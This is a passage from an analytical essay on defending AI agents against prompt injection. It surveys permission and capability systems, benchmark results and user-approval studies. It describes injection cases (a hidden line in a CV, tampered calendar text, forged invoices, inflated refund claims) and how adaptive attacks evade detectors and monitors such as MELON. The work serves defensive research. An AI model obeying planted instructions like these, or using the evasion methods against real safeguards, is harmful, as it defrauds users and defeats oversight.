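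Browsers may be easier to secure than whole desktops, because a browser's effects on other sites pass through web requests, which software can inspect. Foerster and colleagues cite ceLLMate, a system that applies policies to those requests. They see no equivalent layer for clicks in desktop programs and leave translating clicks into meaningful actions to future work.

### Harm through text alone

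An attacker may not need the agent to take any action. In a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C describes a system that scores job applicants' CVs. A candidate hides a line in their CV telling the model to approve it for interview. The model needs no tools to return a favourable score, and a recruiter then invites the candidate.

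Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give an example that involves a tool. A user asks an assistant to send today's schedule to their boss. The plan fixes the recipient, so an attacker who plants text in a calendar entry can't redirect the email, but can change its body. An attacker could also keep an urgent message out of an inbox summary, or have the assistant ask a colleague to approve a security-sensitive step. The colleague would see a request from a familiar account. Every permission check would pass, because the user did want an email sent to that person.

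Restricting the form of the answer helps somewhat. A score from 1 to 10 can't contain a malicious link, though it can still be wrong. A provenance label can warn the reader that a summary draws on untrusted mail, but every accurate summary of that mail would carry the same warning, and people would probably stop noticing it. The assistant could show the original passages beside the summary, but this protects only readers who check them.

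An assistant can make forged messages more effective, which is a reason to count such deception against a security design even though forgery is much older than assistants. The assistant may leave out the odd phrasing or unfamiliar address that would have made a careful reader suspicious, and it presents the attacker's claim in its own voice.

Official guidance does not always treat this channel as dangerous. According to ITPro's *NCSC talks up agents for cyber defense*, the NCSC published a framework in September 2026 for choosing which defensive security tasks to automate, and it found that the lowest-risk tasks often involve advising a person instead of changing a system. That makes sense when the main worry is that an agent will break something, but it is less reassuring when an attacker wrote part of what the agent read and the person cannot independently check the advice.

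### Layered defence

If no mechanism can guarantee safety, an organisation can combine several imperfect protections and limit the damage an attack could do. David C argues for this approach by comparing prompt injection with SQL injection, where an attacker types database commands into a web form, for example. Programmers solved this by sending the user's text to the database separately from the commands. A language model has no such separation, because it only predicts the next piece of text from everything before it. David C calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy" and thinks developers may never fully prevent prompt injection.

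He first recommends making developers and security teams aware of the problem. In the design, he relies more on ordinary software that limits what the system can do than on keeping malicious text away from the model, and he cites CaMeL and the design patterns paper as work in that direction. He then recommends techniques that make the model harder to deceive, and logs that let staff spot an attack in progress. Failed tool calls are useful warnings, since an attacker will probably need several tries. If an organisation can't tolerate the remaining risk, he suggests that the job may not suit a language model. He disagrees with the designers of capability systems more about how much confidence these designs justify than about what to build.

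He also endorses a rule, from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that when a model reads text from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's. In the consultant example, a stranger can't add people to the firm's project call, so an assistant that has read a stranger's email couldn't either. This rule amounts to the strict policy and has the same drawback.

Better-trained models are the most appealing layer because they don't block legitimate work. On AgentDyn, Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed 71.7% of tasks without any added defence, and 0.9% of attacks succeeded. No system-level defence in the study came close to that combination. When Li and colleagues tailored attacks to their scenarios, the success rate rose to 3.0% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and 5.6% for GPT-5.1. They warn that their attacks are weak against the latest models and that developers have probably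 trained those models on the standard templates. Even 3% may be too high for a mailbox that anyone can write to. If each message had an independent 3% chance of working, an attacker who sent 23 messages would have about an even chance of succeeding at least once.

Some low attack success rates may also reflect agents that lacked the skill to finish the attacker's task. *AgentDrift* (2026) cites results from WASP, a test of web agents, in which planted text diverted the agents in 17% to 86% of cases, but they completed the attacker's full goal in at most 16%. If limited ability explains part of this gap, more capable agents will narrow it unless they also become harder to divert.

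Detectors helped little on AgentDyn. With GPT-4o, the detector PIGuard reduced task completion from 53.3% to 10.0% even without an attack, because it misclassified helpful instructions as malicious. PromptGuard 2 left completion at 60.0% without an attack, but 27.2% of attacks still succeeded. When it detected an attack, it discarded the whole tool output, including the information the agent needed, and completion under attack fell to 20.8%. Combining such detectors would increase false alarms as well as protection.

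Another layer limits which powers an agent has at the same time. *The hidden dangers of agentic AI deployments*, a guide from the law firm Mishcon de Reya, describes the "Rule of Two", under which an agent should have no more than two of three high-risk capabilities in one session: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with or affect the outside world. An agent that needs all three should work under supervision. The rule is simple enough for a manager to apply without understanding provenance labels. But the invoice assistant needs all three to do its job, as does almost any assistant that answers email. Two can also be enough for serious harm. If an agent reads public bug reports and can publish code, an attacker could make it publish something malicious even if it has no access to private data.

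Government guidance in 2026 has mostly followed the layered approach. In May, the Australian Cyber Security Centre (2026) and its international partners told organisations to introduce agents gradually and limit them to low-risk tasks, with strict control of privileges, continuous monitoring and human oversight. The NCSC issued interim advice in August, after publicised incidents in which models took unsanctioned actions. *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that the NCSC urged sandboxing, oversight and tight access controls. Professional Security's *NCSC, comments on agentic AI* adds that an organisation should always be able to halt an agent immediately, and should add safeguards beyond the model's own wherever a failure would do more harm than it can tolerate. Ollie Whitehouse, the NCSC's chief technology officer, warned in a statement from the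 agency that detecting incidents after the fact would not be enough on its own.

This advice is sensible, but an organisation can't use it to work out how much risk remains. Two agents could both have a sandbox, monitoring and an off switch, yet one could be far easier to steal from.

### Narrow work and bounded losses

Defenders of restricted designs can accept much of this argument and still deny that it matters for most deployments. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think it very unlikely that untrusted data should determine which actions an email and calendar assistant takes, or their order. Telling regular collaborators about a holiday, for instance, requires a flexible list of recipients but no instructions from anyone's email. Foerster and colleagues similarly conclude that many computer tasks depend less on what appears on screen than researchers had assumed, because a good planner can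 anticipate the likely situations. The NCSC, in May 2026 guidance quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Publishes Guidance on Securing Agentic AI Use*, expects agents to bring benefits particularly where tasks are "repetitive, well-understood and low risk", which are also the tasks for which somebody can write an accurate grant of authority.

A general-purpose assistant could receive a narrow set of permissions for each request instead of one broad grant, much as CapScope did for each repair with a small reduction in completed work. But a person or program would have to choose the right permissions every time, and requests such as "deal with my email" give little indication of which ones are needed. Neither Beurer-Kellner and colleagues nor Foerster and colleagues measured how often real users make such requests. If they are rare, an assistant can refer them to a person and remain useful.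 If people buy assistants mainly to handle them, the restricted designs remove much of what they are paying for.

Where an agent must act on a stranger's message, limiting the damage may be enough. An assistant could be allowed to add up to ten provisional calendar entries a day, with no invitations or attachments. An attacker could fill the calendar with nonsense entries, but the owner could delete them. A firm might likewise accept losing up to €5,000 a month to forged invoices if the assistant saves more than that in wages. A forwarding object could enforce either limit.

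Setting the limit is harder when the loss isn't money. Nobody can take back a client list after an attacker has read it, and one bad line of published code can reach every customer. ITPro reports that Dave Chismon, the NCSC's chief technology officer for architecture, told defenders that proving deterministically that "low risk" actions are low risk still needs research. Even a loss that each firm can tolerate may add up to a large gain for an attacker who targets many firms. If a thousand firms use the same assistant and each tolerates a loss of €5,000 a month, one reliable forgery could be worth €5 million a month.

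## Do the defences hold when attackers adapt?

Most of the attack success rates quoted for agent defences come from static tests, which run a fixed set of attacks regardless of the defence. CaMeL, Progent, TACIT and AgentCap all had low rates on AgentDojo, whose planted instructions predate all four systems. A real attacker can read the paper describing a defence, run a copy of the defence, and design or optimise an attack to get past it. Such adaptive attacks have defeated several defences that looked nearly perfect in static tests.

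### Why a fixed set of attacks misleads

Suppose the firm with the invoice assistant buys a detector that scans incoming mail for planted instructions. The vendor reports that the detector caught all 500 planted instructions in a public collection. An attacker with access to the same detector can keep rewording an instruction until the detector no longer flags it. The attacker then sends the firm only that version, which is unlike anything in the vendor's test.

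*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) applied this process to twelve published defences. Some target prompt injection and others target jailbreaks, in which users themselves try to get harmful output from a model. The original papers reported attack success rates near zero for most of the defences.

In each automated attack, the attacker's program repeatedly proposes several texts, runs them against the defended system, scores the results and uses the best texts to produce the next batch. In the search version, a language model rewrites the most promising texts. The reinforcement-learning version also uses the scores to train the model that writes them. Nasr and colleagues assumed that the attacker knows how the defence works and has plenty of computing power, because a defence that attackers can break with a day's computing on a cluster of processors offers little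 lasting protection. They also ran a competition in which more than 500 people attacked some of the defences by hand.

| Approach | Defences | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Add instructions or markers to the prompt | Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching, RPO | Above 95% for all three |
| Train the model on known attacks | StruQ, MetaSecAlign, Circuit Breakers | 96% to 100% |
| Scan text with a separate detector | Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor, PIGuard | Above 90% for three, 71% for PIGuard |
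| Test the model with information hidden from the attacker | Data Sentinel, MELON | Data Sentinel failed in every case; 76% to 95% for MELON |

The rows can't be used to rank the defences, because Nasr and colleagues kept each defence's original benchmark where they could. Knowing how a defence works can help an attacker, as it did with MELON. MELON runs the agent a second time with a neutral request in place of the user's, and flags an injection if the same tool calls appear in both runs. The search reached a 76% success rate without knowing how MELON worked. With that knowledge, it found text that made the agent behave differently in the second run, and success rose to 95%.

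The danger is greater than even these automated attacks show. On a subset of scenarios, the search succeeded in 69%, while the human attackers collectively succeeded in all of them.

All twelve defences change the model's prompt, train the model, or try to recognise malicious text and behaviour. None limits which tools the agent can call or with which arguments. The study didn't test CaMeL, which five of the researchers also helped develop. It therefore doesn't show that permission checks fail. MetaSecAlign let through 2% of AgentDojo's own attacks but 96% of the adaptive ones, so a low attack success rate on AgentDojo proves little about whether a defence will hold when attackers adapt.

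A test can also stop too early. Deep, Emmons and colleagues (2026), in *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*, put three secrets in a chatbot's hidden instructions and had an automated attacker send ten messages a round, learning from the replies. After 25 rounds, none of the protected configurations had leaked all three secrets. When the attacks continued, the five defences that relied on the model alone or on screening its input failed after 39 to 277 rounds. Leaks usually stayed small for a long time and then became nearly total in a single round. A test that ended after 200 rounds would have made two of these defences look much stronger than they were.

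Even against well-trained models, attackers succeed more often when they can try repeatedly. Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's results for Claude Opus 4.5, an older model, against adaptive attacks on coding agents. The attacker succeeded in 4.7% of cases with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred.

### Adaptive attacks on checks outside the model

A permission check gives this kind of search much less feedback than a detector, whose score the search can lower a little at a time. If the firm's payment software accepts only account numbers on a list, rewording an invoice doesn't bring the attacker's number any closer to acceptance.

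The attacker has to attack something else, such as a language model that writes or revises the rules, the software that assigns provenance labels, the person who approves exceptions, or flaws and side channels in the checking code. The attacker can also choose a harmful goal that the rules already permit. A serious adaptive test would try all of these, but experiments so far have covered only a few.

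In Progent, the obvious target is the model that revises the policy as the task proceeds. Shi and colleagues attacked this model in their own tests, again using GPT-4o and automatically approving every expansion. Narisetty and colleagues report that the attacks succeeded roughly 0.5% to 4.2% of the time, with task completion largely preserved.

Narisetty and colleagues then ran an independent test on a much weaker model, Qwen2.5-7B, which served both as the agent and as Progent's policy writer. They paired the first eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo applications with every attacker goal for that application. Their adaptive attack was a single hand-written template that presented the harmful action as a routine, already authorised step, so that the policy writer would permit it. They ran the study three times, and the table gives the average attack success rates.

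| Application | No defence, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent reduced the mean attack success rate about sixfold, and the adaptive template did not raise it. But the workspace result can't show whether Progent helps, because the small model did not act on the planted text there even without a defence. Over banking and Slack alone, Progent reduced the mean from 38.7% to 6.4% with the standard attack and 4.0% with the adaptive one.

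An attack tailored to a defence should do at least as well as a generic one, so the lower figure suggests that the template was poor. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that making the planted text sound harmless enough for the policy writer also made the agent less likely to obey it. A real attacker could use whichever text worked better in each application, which would give success rates of 3.7% in banking and 10.8% in Slack, and an average of 4.8% over the three applications.

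Progent also reduced the share of user tasks completed during attacks, from 45.2% without a defence to 27.1%. Completion was unaffected in banking but fell by half or more in Slack and by about half in the workspace. Each task needed around 15 times as many model calls, because the policy writer ran after every tool call.

This evidence is encouraging but weak. The attacker knew how Progent worked but had no loop for improving the attack, and such loops broke the twelve earlier defences. The three repetitions used identical tasks, so their close agreement shows that the measurement is stable, but not that the result would hold for other tasks. Narisetty and colleagues work for a company that builds security tools on the same principle, and they describe the results as preliminary.

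### Persistent attacks on a filter in code

Deep and colleagues did use an optimising attacker against a check written in ordinary code. Besides the defences that broke, they tested a filter that blocks any reply containing pieces of the hidden instructions. They ran the filter three times alone and three times with the other defences, for 500 rounds each time, and it let nothing through. They report a total of 15,000 attacks, although six runs of 5,000 attacks would make 30,000.

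The scoring method makes this result much less impressive. The program that counted leaks searched replies for the secrets, the chatbot's name and long phrases copied from the hidden instructions, and the filter searched for much the same strings. A reply that gave a secret in another form could have escaped both and counted as a success for the defence. The attacking program learned from this score, so it got no reward for finding such a reply.

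Without the filter, the other defences performed better than the paper's summary implies. With all of them combined, 23 of 5,000 attacks leaked something, and the worst leak scored 0.10. A single secret scored 0.30, so none of those attacks revealed a complete secret that the scoring could recognise. Deep and colleagues, most of whom work for a company that sells testing tools, still conclude that security boundaries belong in application code.

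Deep and colleagues' conclusion is sound whatever the count, because persuasion can't change the result of comparing two strings. But the filter protects only the strings it looks for, whereas a payment check needs only a list of accepted accounts and can refuse all others. They also advise against putting secrets in a model's instructions. The invoice assistant's harness follows this advice by keeping the bank credentials where the model can't read them, so the model can't reveal them.

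### Attacks that use the expected tools

Most attacks in AgentDojo try to make the agent take an extra action, such as forwarding an email when the user asked for a summary of appointments. A permission check can often block the extra action because the task doesn't need it. An attacker who knows about the check has good reason to alter an action the task does need instead.

*Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) introduces a benchmark built around such attacks, which it terms task tampering. In one case, the user asks an agent to resolve a dispute over a damaged item and to take the refund amount from the platform's order record, which authorises $899.99. The buyer's evidence gives a false reason for refunding $1,074.99. The task already requires the agent to read the evidence and issue a refund, so the attack only changes the amount and needs no new tool or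 step.

Zhang and colleagues count planted text as an injection when it is meant to determine a decision that its source has no authority over. If the user had asked only what reason the buyer gave, a false reason would have been ordinary misinformation. In every case, therefore, the user's request settles the decision or names a record or procedure that does, so the agent can always find the right answer. This makes the test fair, but it leaves out harder situations, such as a forged invoice from an unknown company when the firm has no independent record of what it owes.

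The benchmark has 90 cases set in office work, software maintenance and a marketplace. For each case, the researchers wrote several texts meant to cause the same harmful result in different ways. In the refund case, the buyer could demand the higher sum, cite a policy that doesn't exist, warn of a penalty for paying less, or misstate what the order record authorises. These texts gave 1,433 attacked runs for each model and defence. The table shows averages over five models, including DeepSeek V3.1 and Claude Sonnet 4.5.

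| Defence | Attack success | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 17.0% | 95.3% | 83.7% |
| Repeating the user's request | 10.4% | 98.5% | 89.4% |
| DRIFT, text removal only | 6.6% | 98.0% | 93.3% |
| DRIFT, complete | 7.0% | 88.9% | 83.4% |
| Progent | 15.4% | 74.9% | 65.0% |
| CaMeL | 1.3% | 13.3% | 13.9% |

Progent's improvement over no defence was too small to distinguish from chance. Zhang and colleagues examined runs with two of the models, in which Progent blocked 8 of the agents' 116 tampered calls. All 8 blocks came from rules about an argument's value and none from the list of permitted tools, as one would expect when the attack uses a tool the task needs.

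CaMeL had by far the lowest attack success rate, at 1.3%, but it completed only 60 of 450 tasks (13.3%) when nobody was attacking. Most of its apparent protection could come from inactivity, because an agent that rarely finishes tasks also rarely carries out an attacker's instructions. If CaMeL had stopped actions at random until task completion fell from 95.3% to 13.3%, attack success would have fallen to about 2.4%. The observed rate is lower, so the labels may have stopped some attacks.

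Zhang and colleagues wrote CaMeL's policies themselves and required values such as recipients and amounts to come from trusted fields. They also adapted the other defences to their own agent, so the results may not match those of the original systems. CaMeL probably did badly partly because its planner must write a program before it reads the evidence. The same weakness is why it completed no tasks on AgentDyn.

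DRIFT's text removal, which uses a language model to find and delete planted instructions, has the best balance in the table. Direct demands succeeded only 2.4% of the time against it, but false statements about the facts still succeeded 12.1% of the time. More importantly, it is the kind of defence that adaptive attacks have broken. Zhang and colleagues rewrote some attacks to evade a separate detector and found only small changes in their success against DRIFT, but they did not optimise the attacks against DRIFT itself. Repeating the user's request also did fairly well in the table, with attacks succeeding 10.4% of the time, but the same technique, under the name Prompt Sandwiching, failed against more than 95% of the optimised attacks on AgentDojo.

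Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil is in the Context*, found a similar gap by changing AgentDojo's cases. They first classified attacks by nine yes-or-no properties, such as whether the user can see the planted text, whether the attack takes effect only under a certain condition, and whether it is meant to alter the agent's stored memory. Each pair of properties has four possible combinations of answers, which makes 144 across all pairs. Nineteen of these appeared in none of the nine benchmarks they examined.

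They then took 40 user tasks from AgentDojo's workspace, each with one randomly chosen attack. With GPT-5.6-Luna as the agent, none of the 40 attacks worked, even without a defence. A language model then rewrote each case so that the attack concerned the subject of the user's task, applied only under a stated condition, and changed the content of an action without changing the sequence of actions. Seven of the 40 rewritten attacks (17.5%) succeeded against the undefended agent. With MELON as the defence, the success rate was slightly higher, at 20%.

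One of the 40 attacks (2.5%) succeeded against CaMeL, and the agent completed 27.5% of the users' tasks. This fits CaMeL's design, which prevents planted text from adding steps but allows some untrusted values into steps already planned. However, with so few cases and only one model, the difference of six attacks is a rough estimate. The rewritten cases were also not fully adaptive, because the researchers chose properties missing from the benchmark and did not optimise the attacks against CaMeL.

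### Why the results differ

Progent stopped most attacks in one study and almost none in another, and the type of attack explains much of the difference. A rule can stop a wrong refund or a misleading sentence in an expected email only if it specifies the correct value. In 38 of Zhang and colleagues' 90 cases, the harm lay in text the agent wrote, such as a message or a project note, and few policies restrict what such text contains.

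Better policies could help with the other 52. A rule that takes the refund amount only from the order record would block the buyer's figure, however persuasive the evidence was. Progent's model-written rules were seldom this specific. Where Progent reduced attack success, it did so largely by stopping the agent's work. In the office setting, attack success fell from 14.8% to 6.4%, but ordinary task completion fell almost as steeply, from 92.1% to 43.6%. In software maintenance and the marketplace, the agent still completed nearly nine in ten tasks, but Progent did not reduce attack success.

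Tools can also be too coarse for useful rules. *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested agents whose only tool runs one shell command per turn. The agents used it to edit files, install packages and contact other machines while completing 40 long tasks, such as repairing or deploying software. The 56 attack scenarios included stealing keys, corrupting data and introducing untrusted packages. Across 19 models, attacks succeeded on average 19.6% of the time as judged by a language model, and 15.4% according to automatic checks.

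In this setting, a rule that permits the shell tool permits everything the shell can do, and a harness that inspects the text of each command, as CapScope does, still needs a sandbox. On a selection of cases where attacks succeeded unusually often, adding protective instructions to the prompt reduced the attack success rate from 58.2% to 14.3%. That is a large improvement against a fixed set of attacks, but Nasr and colleagues' results give little reason to expect it to hold against a determined attacker.

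### Optimised attacks on permitted actions

None of these experiments tested an attacker who optimises against a permission system while pursuing goals that the system allows. Nasr and colleagues optimised their attacks but did not test permission systems. The adaptive tests of Progent targeted its policy writer and did not try to cause harm within an unchanged policy. Zhang and colleagues and Chang and colleagues studied attacks that use expected actions, but did not optimise them against Progent or CaMeL. Narisetty and colleagues say their next experiment will be an adaptive attack confined to authorised actions. None of the studies tested references held by code, so they provide no direct evidence about TACIT or other object-capability designs.

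An attacker who optimises the planted text should gain nothing outside the grant if every action passes through the check, the check has no flaws, and no model or person can widen the grant. Inside the grant, the check approves the action, so only the model and any defences around it can stop the attack. Adaptive attacks have repeatedly raised success rates against these components from near zero to above 90%. Newer models may resist better, but a low attack success rate on a static benchmark is not evidence that they do.

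Attackers can succeed much more often just by trying several texts. Zhang and colleagues' benchmark contains about 15 differently worded texts per case, not counting those that combine several arguments. Without a defence, a single text worked only about one time in six, but at least one of them worked in 51 of the 90 cases for the average model. With Progent, at least one worked in 43 cases, and with CaMeL in 6. An attacker who could observe the results and write new texts would probably do better.

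Provenance tracking changes which parts of an action an adaptive attacker can influence. An attacker who optimises the text of a forged invoice can't change a correct provenance label on its account number, but may gain influence over anything the policy accepts from untrusted sources. A firm using these systems should therefore set its limits on the assumption that an attacker can obtain the worst values the policy allows from those sources.

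## Who grants the authority, and can that step be deceived?

Every check described so far enforces a grant that a person or program chose. An attacker who can't get past the check can try to influence that choice instead.

Most grants come from a developer who writes a fixed policy, a model that predicts what a request needs, or a user who approves actions while the agent runs. People usually notice when a grant is too narrow because it stops legitimate work, but a grant that is too wide appears to work well until an attack or an accident uses the extra authority.

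| Source of the grant | Typical error | How the error shows |
|---|---|---|
| Developer's fixed policy | It covers every task the agent might do, so it is too wide for any one of them | Usually nothing fails until an attack |
| Model's prediction | It omits a permission the task needs, or takes a value from text the user didn't write | Refused calls and unfinished tasks, or a rule that names the attacker |
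| User's approval | The user misunderstands the action or stops reading the prompts | The log records consent |

### Fixed policies

Many online services use OAuth, a standard that lets a user give a program limited access to an account. The service's developers define a list of permissions, called scopes, and the program requests the ones it needs. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) points out that a scope can permit bank transfers but can't limit them to sending Bob $100, so an assistant with that scope can pay anyone.

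In *Lingering Authority*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) compared fixed policies with PORTICO, a system for coding agents that enforces a contract written for each task. In 17 scenarios, the agent could reach tempting resources outside its task. It broke the contract in every run with full access, in 86% of runs with a sandbox, and in 82% with a fixed list of permitted tools and paths. PORTICO allowed no violations. But the same contract determined both what PORTICO blocked and what counted as a violation, so this result shows that PORTICO enforced the contract, but not that the contract was right.

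Narrow contracts reduced completion on another 37 tasks, many of which needed files outside the initial permissions. An agent restricted to those permissions completed 21% of the tasks, compared with 97% under the fixed list. When the agent could also request extra permissions that the contract had declared in advance, it completed 87%.

### Permissions predicted from the request

In CapScope, Bouras and colleagues have a model predict a task's permissions before it sees any file contents, so the prediction can miss some that the task needs. Another approach is to calculate the smallest set of permissions sufficient for the task.

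MiniScope finds the smallest set of OAuth privileges a task needs. Some scopes include others, as permission to manage a mailbox includes permission to read it, and MiniScope reconstructs this hierarchy from the services' OAuth settings. It then selects the privileges with an integer program, a standard type of optimisation problem. In a simple program of this type, each scope `s` has a weight `c_s`, and `x_s` is 1 if the grant includes the scope and 0 if it doesn't. The solver minimises the total weight `Σ c_s x_s` while ensuring that at least one chosen scope covers each tool call the task requires.

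There may be more than one smallest grant. Suppose an agent has to find a contract that is both attached to an email and stored in a shared folder. Permission to read either the mailbox or the folder would be enough, and neither permission includes the other. The solver chooses between them using the weights assigned to each permission, so whoever sets the weights is judging which access is more dangerous. According to *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026), MiniScope's developers do not discuss whether the optimum is unique. The calculation also needs a correct list of tool calls. If an attacker has added a call to the list, the solver will find the least privilege that allows the attacker's call as well.

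An agent's choice of tools is a poor guide to the authority it needs. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) cites a 544-scenario test in which 6 of 11 agents chose a tool with more privilege than necessary in over 30% of cases. Natural-language requests can also be ambiguous, and *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) warns that a manipulated prompt may lead the system to request a broader permission than the user intended.

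Users can instead write rules in plain language, such as "never delete anything", but a model then has to work out which tools delete things. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tested Claude Sonnet 5 on this task with 120 tools, chosen to include ambiguous and high-stakes ones. A simulated "never" rule missed 14% of the tools it should have blocked and wrongly blocked 4% of the others. The tools had ordinary descriptions, and Yan did not test misleading ones, which a malicious developer could write.

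### What people approve

Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, reviewed 21 research proposals and tried five commercial agents in May and June 2026. The commercial agents tended towards one of two extremes, either asking for approval frequently or relying on automatic review by a model that users could barely inspect or control. ChatGPT's chat mode required approval for every action that its permissions covered, and users could not give approval in advance. Its agent mode operates a remote browser, for which Michael and Roesner could not set any permissions.

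Yan measured how people respond to such prompts by having 113 participants without professional software backgrounds supervise a simulated assistant through a day of email, travel and errands. The day's goals required 11 of the assistant's 18 actions. The other 7, such as reading private messages or buying a $25 airport lounge pass, went beyond those goals.

In one group, participants decided on each action themselves. In another, a model allowed 8 actions automatically and passed 10 to the participant, including all 7 excessive ones. The remaining participants first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things, and reading private information. The table shows how often participants approved an excessive action when prompted about it.

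| Excessive action | Approved every action by hand | Model screened actions | Wrote their own rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call the airport to confirm a flight | 88.2% | 84.1% | 100.0% |
| Read private messages | 35.3% | 43.2% | 73.9% |
| Read recent bank transactions | 35.3% | 40.9% | 65.2% |
| Buy a lounge pass | 32.4% | 38.6% | 61.3% |
| Post publicly that the user is travelling | 20.6% | 29.5% | 48.4% |
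| All seven actions | 40.3% | 46.1% | 66.8% |

The first group allowed 94.1% of the required actions and 40.3% of the excessive ones, so participants did not approve blindly. Many users might welcome one of the excessive actions, the call to the airport. Without it, the group still allowed 32.4% of the excessive actions, which is a high rate for actions nobody requested.

The group with rules let through the largest share of excessive actions. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so most decisions reached them as prompts, and they approved two-thirds of the excessive actions they saw. This group's approval rate is not strictly comparable with the others', because it saw prompts only where its own rules called for them. But even counting actions that the rules blocked or allowed automatically, 60.4% of excessive actions went ahead. Yan did not establish why this group did worst.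 Participants in all three groups reported feeling in control.

The experiment took about 11 minutes and involved no real money or data, so it reveals little about fatigue. Reports from actual use suggest that fatigue matters. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of problems with agents and files, and user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, users had let the agent act without asking, since they could otherwise face hundreds of prompts in a session. In 31, the prompt was uninformative. A request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code the script contains. Because the study only covers reported problems, it can't show how often approval prevents harm.

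The wording of approval prompts is part of the problem. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) found that most prompts in commercial products show a raw command on a single line. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that people may approve repeatedly because they are tired or under pressure to deliver, not because they trust the agent more. A system that turns repeated approvals into a standing permission could therefore give an agent lasting authority because its user was tired or rushed.

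Asking for approval less often might help. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) simulated a system that asks for approval when untrusted data has influenced an action the rules permit. Attack success fell from 23.1% to 8.7%, with 0.57 approval prompts per ordinary task. However, the reviewer was also simulated, so the improvement depends on the researchers' assumptions about how well people judge prompts.

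None of these studies measures approval under social engineering, where an attacker writes text to get a person to approve a harmful action. Yan's simulated assistant exceeded its task without an attacker, and the prompts described each action neutrally. *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025) comes closer because it used interfaces designed to manipulate users. Its participants did eight tasks alone and supervised OpenAI's Operator agent on eight others. But manipulative web design is a different threat from a fraudster who tailors an invoice to one firm's suppliers.

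This is a serious gap in the evidence, because several designs leave their hardest cases to the user. When CaMeL blocks a payment to the fake cleaning company and leaves the decision to the owner, the prompt might show a plausible name, an amount of €3,000 and an account number. The owner can't detect the fraud from those details. A better prompt would add that the account number appears only in an email and in none of the firm's records, but the same warning would appear for every honest new supplier.

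### Authority from ordinary acts

Capability designers have long tried to avoid separate permission prompts. In their approach, a program starts with no access to the user's files. When it needs a file, the operating system displays a file chooser that the program can't control. The user picks a file, and the system gives the program a reference to only that file. Picking the file both identifies it and grants access, as Hardy's maxim requires.

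Designers call the trusted chooser a powerbox. Miller helped build CapDesk, an experimental desktop that used one. Ka-Ping Yee called the general principle "security by designation" and contrasted it with "security by admonition", in which the system interrupts people with warnings. Roesner and colleagues extended the idea to devices in their 2012 work on user-driven access control. In their design, the operating system places its own camera button inside an app, and pressing it lets the app take a picture. The system must prevent the app from disguising or covering the button, since a user tricked into pressing it would still grant access.

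This works when the user's act identifies the resource. If the owner of the small firm drags a bill onto a "pay" button, that action specifies which bill to pay. If the owner types "pay this week's invoices", the request doesn't identify any bill or account. The assistant could display a trusted list of the payees it has found, but the owner would then have to check each one, much as with an approval prompt. A powerbox infers consent from the user's choices, and a user who delegates an open-ended goal leaves those choices to the assistant.

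IntentCap uses whatever choices the request does contain. Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026), in *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, argue that a capability should last only for the current task, and that each of its details should come from a source entitled to supply it. Their example is a user who selects two PDFs and asks an agent to extract the tables and create one issue in a named GitHub repository. Four sources contribute to the grant:

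- The user's request supplies the files, the repository and any approvals.
- Workflow instructions, such as a stored procedure for extracting tables, supply the steps.
- The tool's definition supplies the form of the call.
- Results from running tools, including the PDF text, supply data for the spreadsheet and the body of the issue.

A model proposes a short-lived, single-use permission, called a lease, to create one issue in a repository. Ordinary code then checks that the repository name matches words in the user's request and that the lease grants no more than the user allowed. If hidden text in a PDF leads the model to name an attacker's repository, the code rejects the lease because the user never mentioned that repository.

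When Zheng and colleagues replayed 3,746 security-sensitive events from four benchmarks, the checker accepted none that it should have refused. When they treated all four sources as equally trusted, it wrongly accepted 94% of a set of 3,823 events. These preliminary results show that the checker depends on distinguishing between the sources, but they don't measure how often an attack would succeed against a running agent. Zheng and colleagues left adaptive attacks on the labels and leases to future work.

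The method also can't fill in a choice the user never made, so it would probably refuse to pay honest new suppliers, as a strict provenance policy would. An incorrect label could still allow the payee to come from the wrong source.

### Authority that outlasts its purpose

A grant can be right at first but become excessive once the work that justified it is finished. *CreepScope* (2026) distinguishes authorising each call correctly from maintaining least privilege over a grant's lifetime.

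PORTICO tries to do both. In Santos-Grueiro's main example, an agent has to add a timeout setting to `src/api.py` and carry it through to `src/serialization.py`. The agent starts with access to the first file, its tests and the program that runs them. When it reaches the second file, it requests access under a rule already in the contract. PORTICO then issues handles, which are references tied to that file, the permitted effect and the current grant. Once the tests pass, PORTICO removes the handles from the agent's list of options and rejects any attempt to reuse them.

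Like Redell's caretaker, this ends the agent's access to the file but doesn't remove the file's name or contents from the agent's memory. Trusted software must generate the events that end a grant. If the model writes that it has finished or needs more time, the grant doesn't change. An attacker who can make the tests fail might still keep a grant open until another event ends it.

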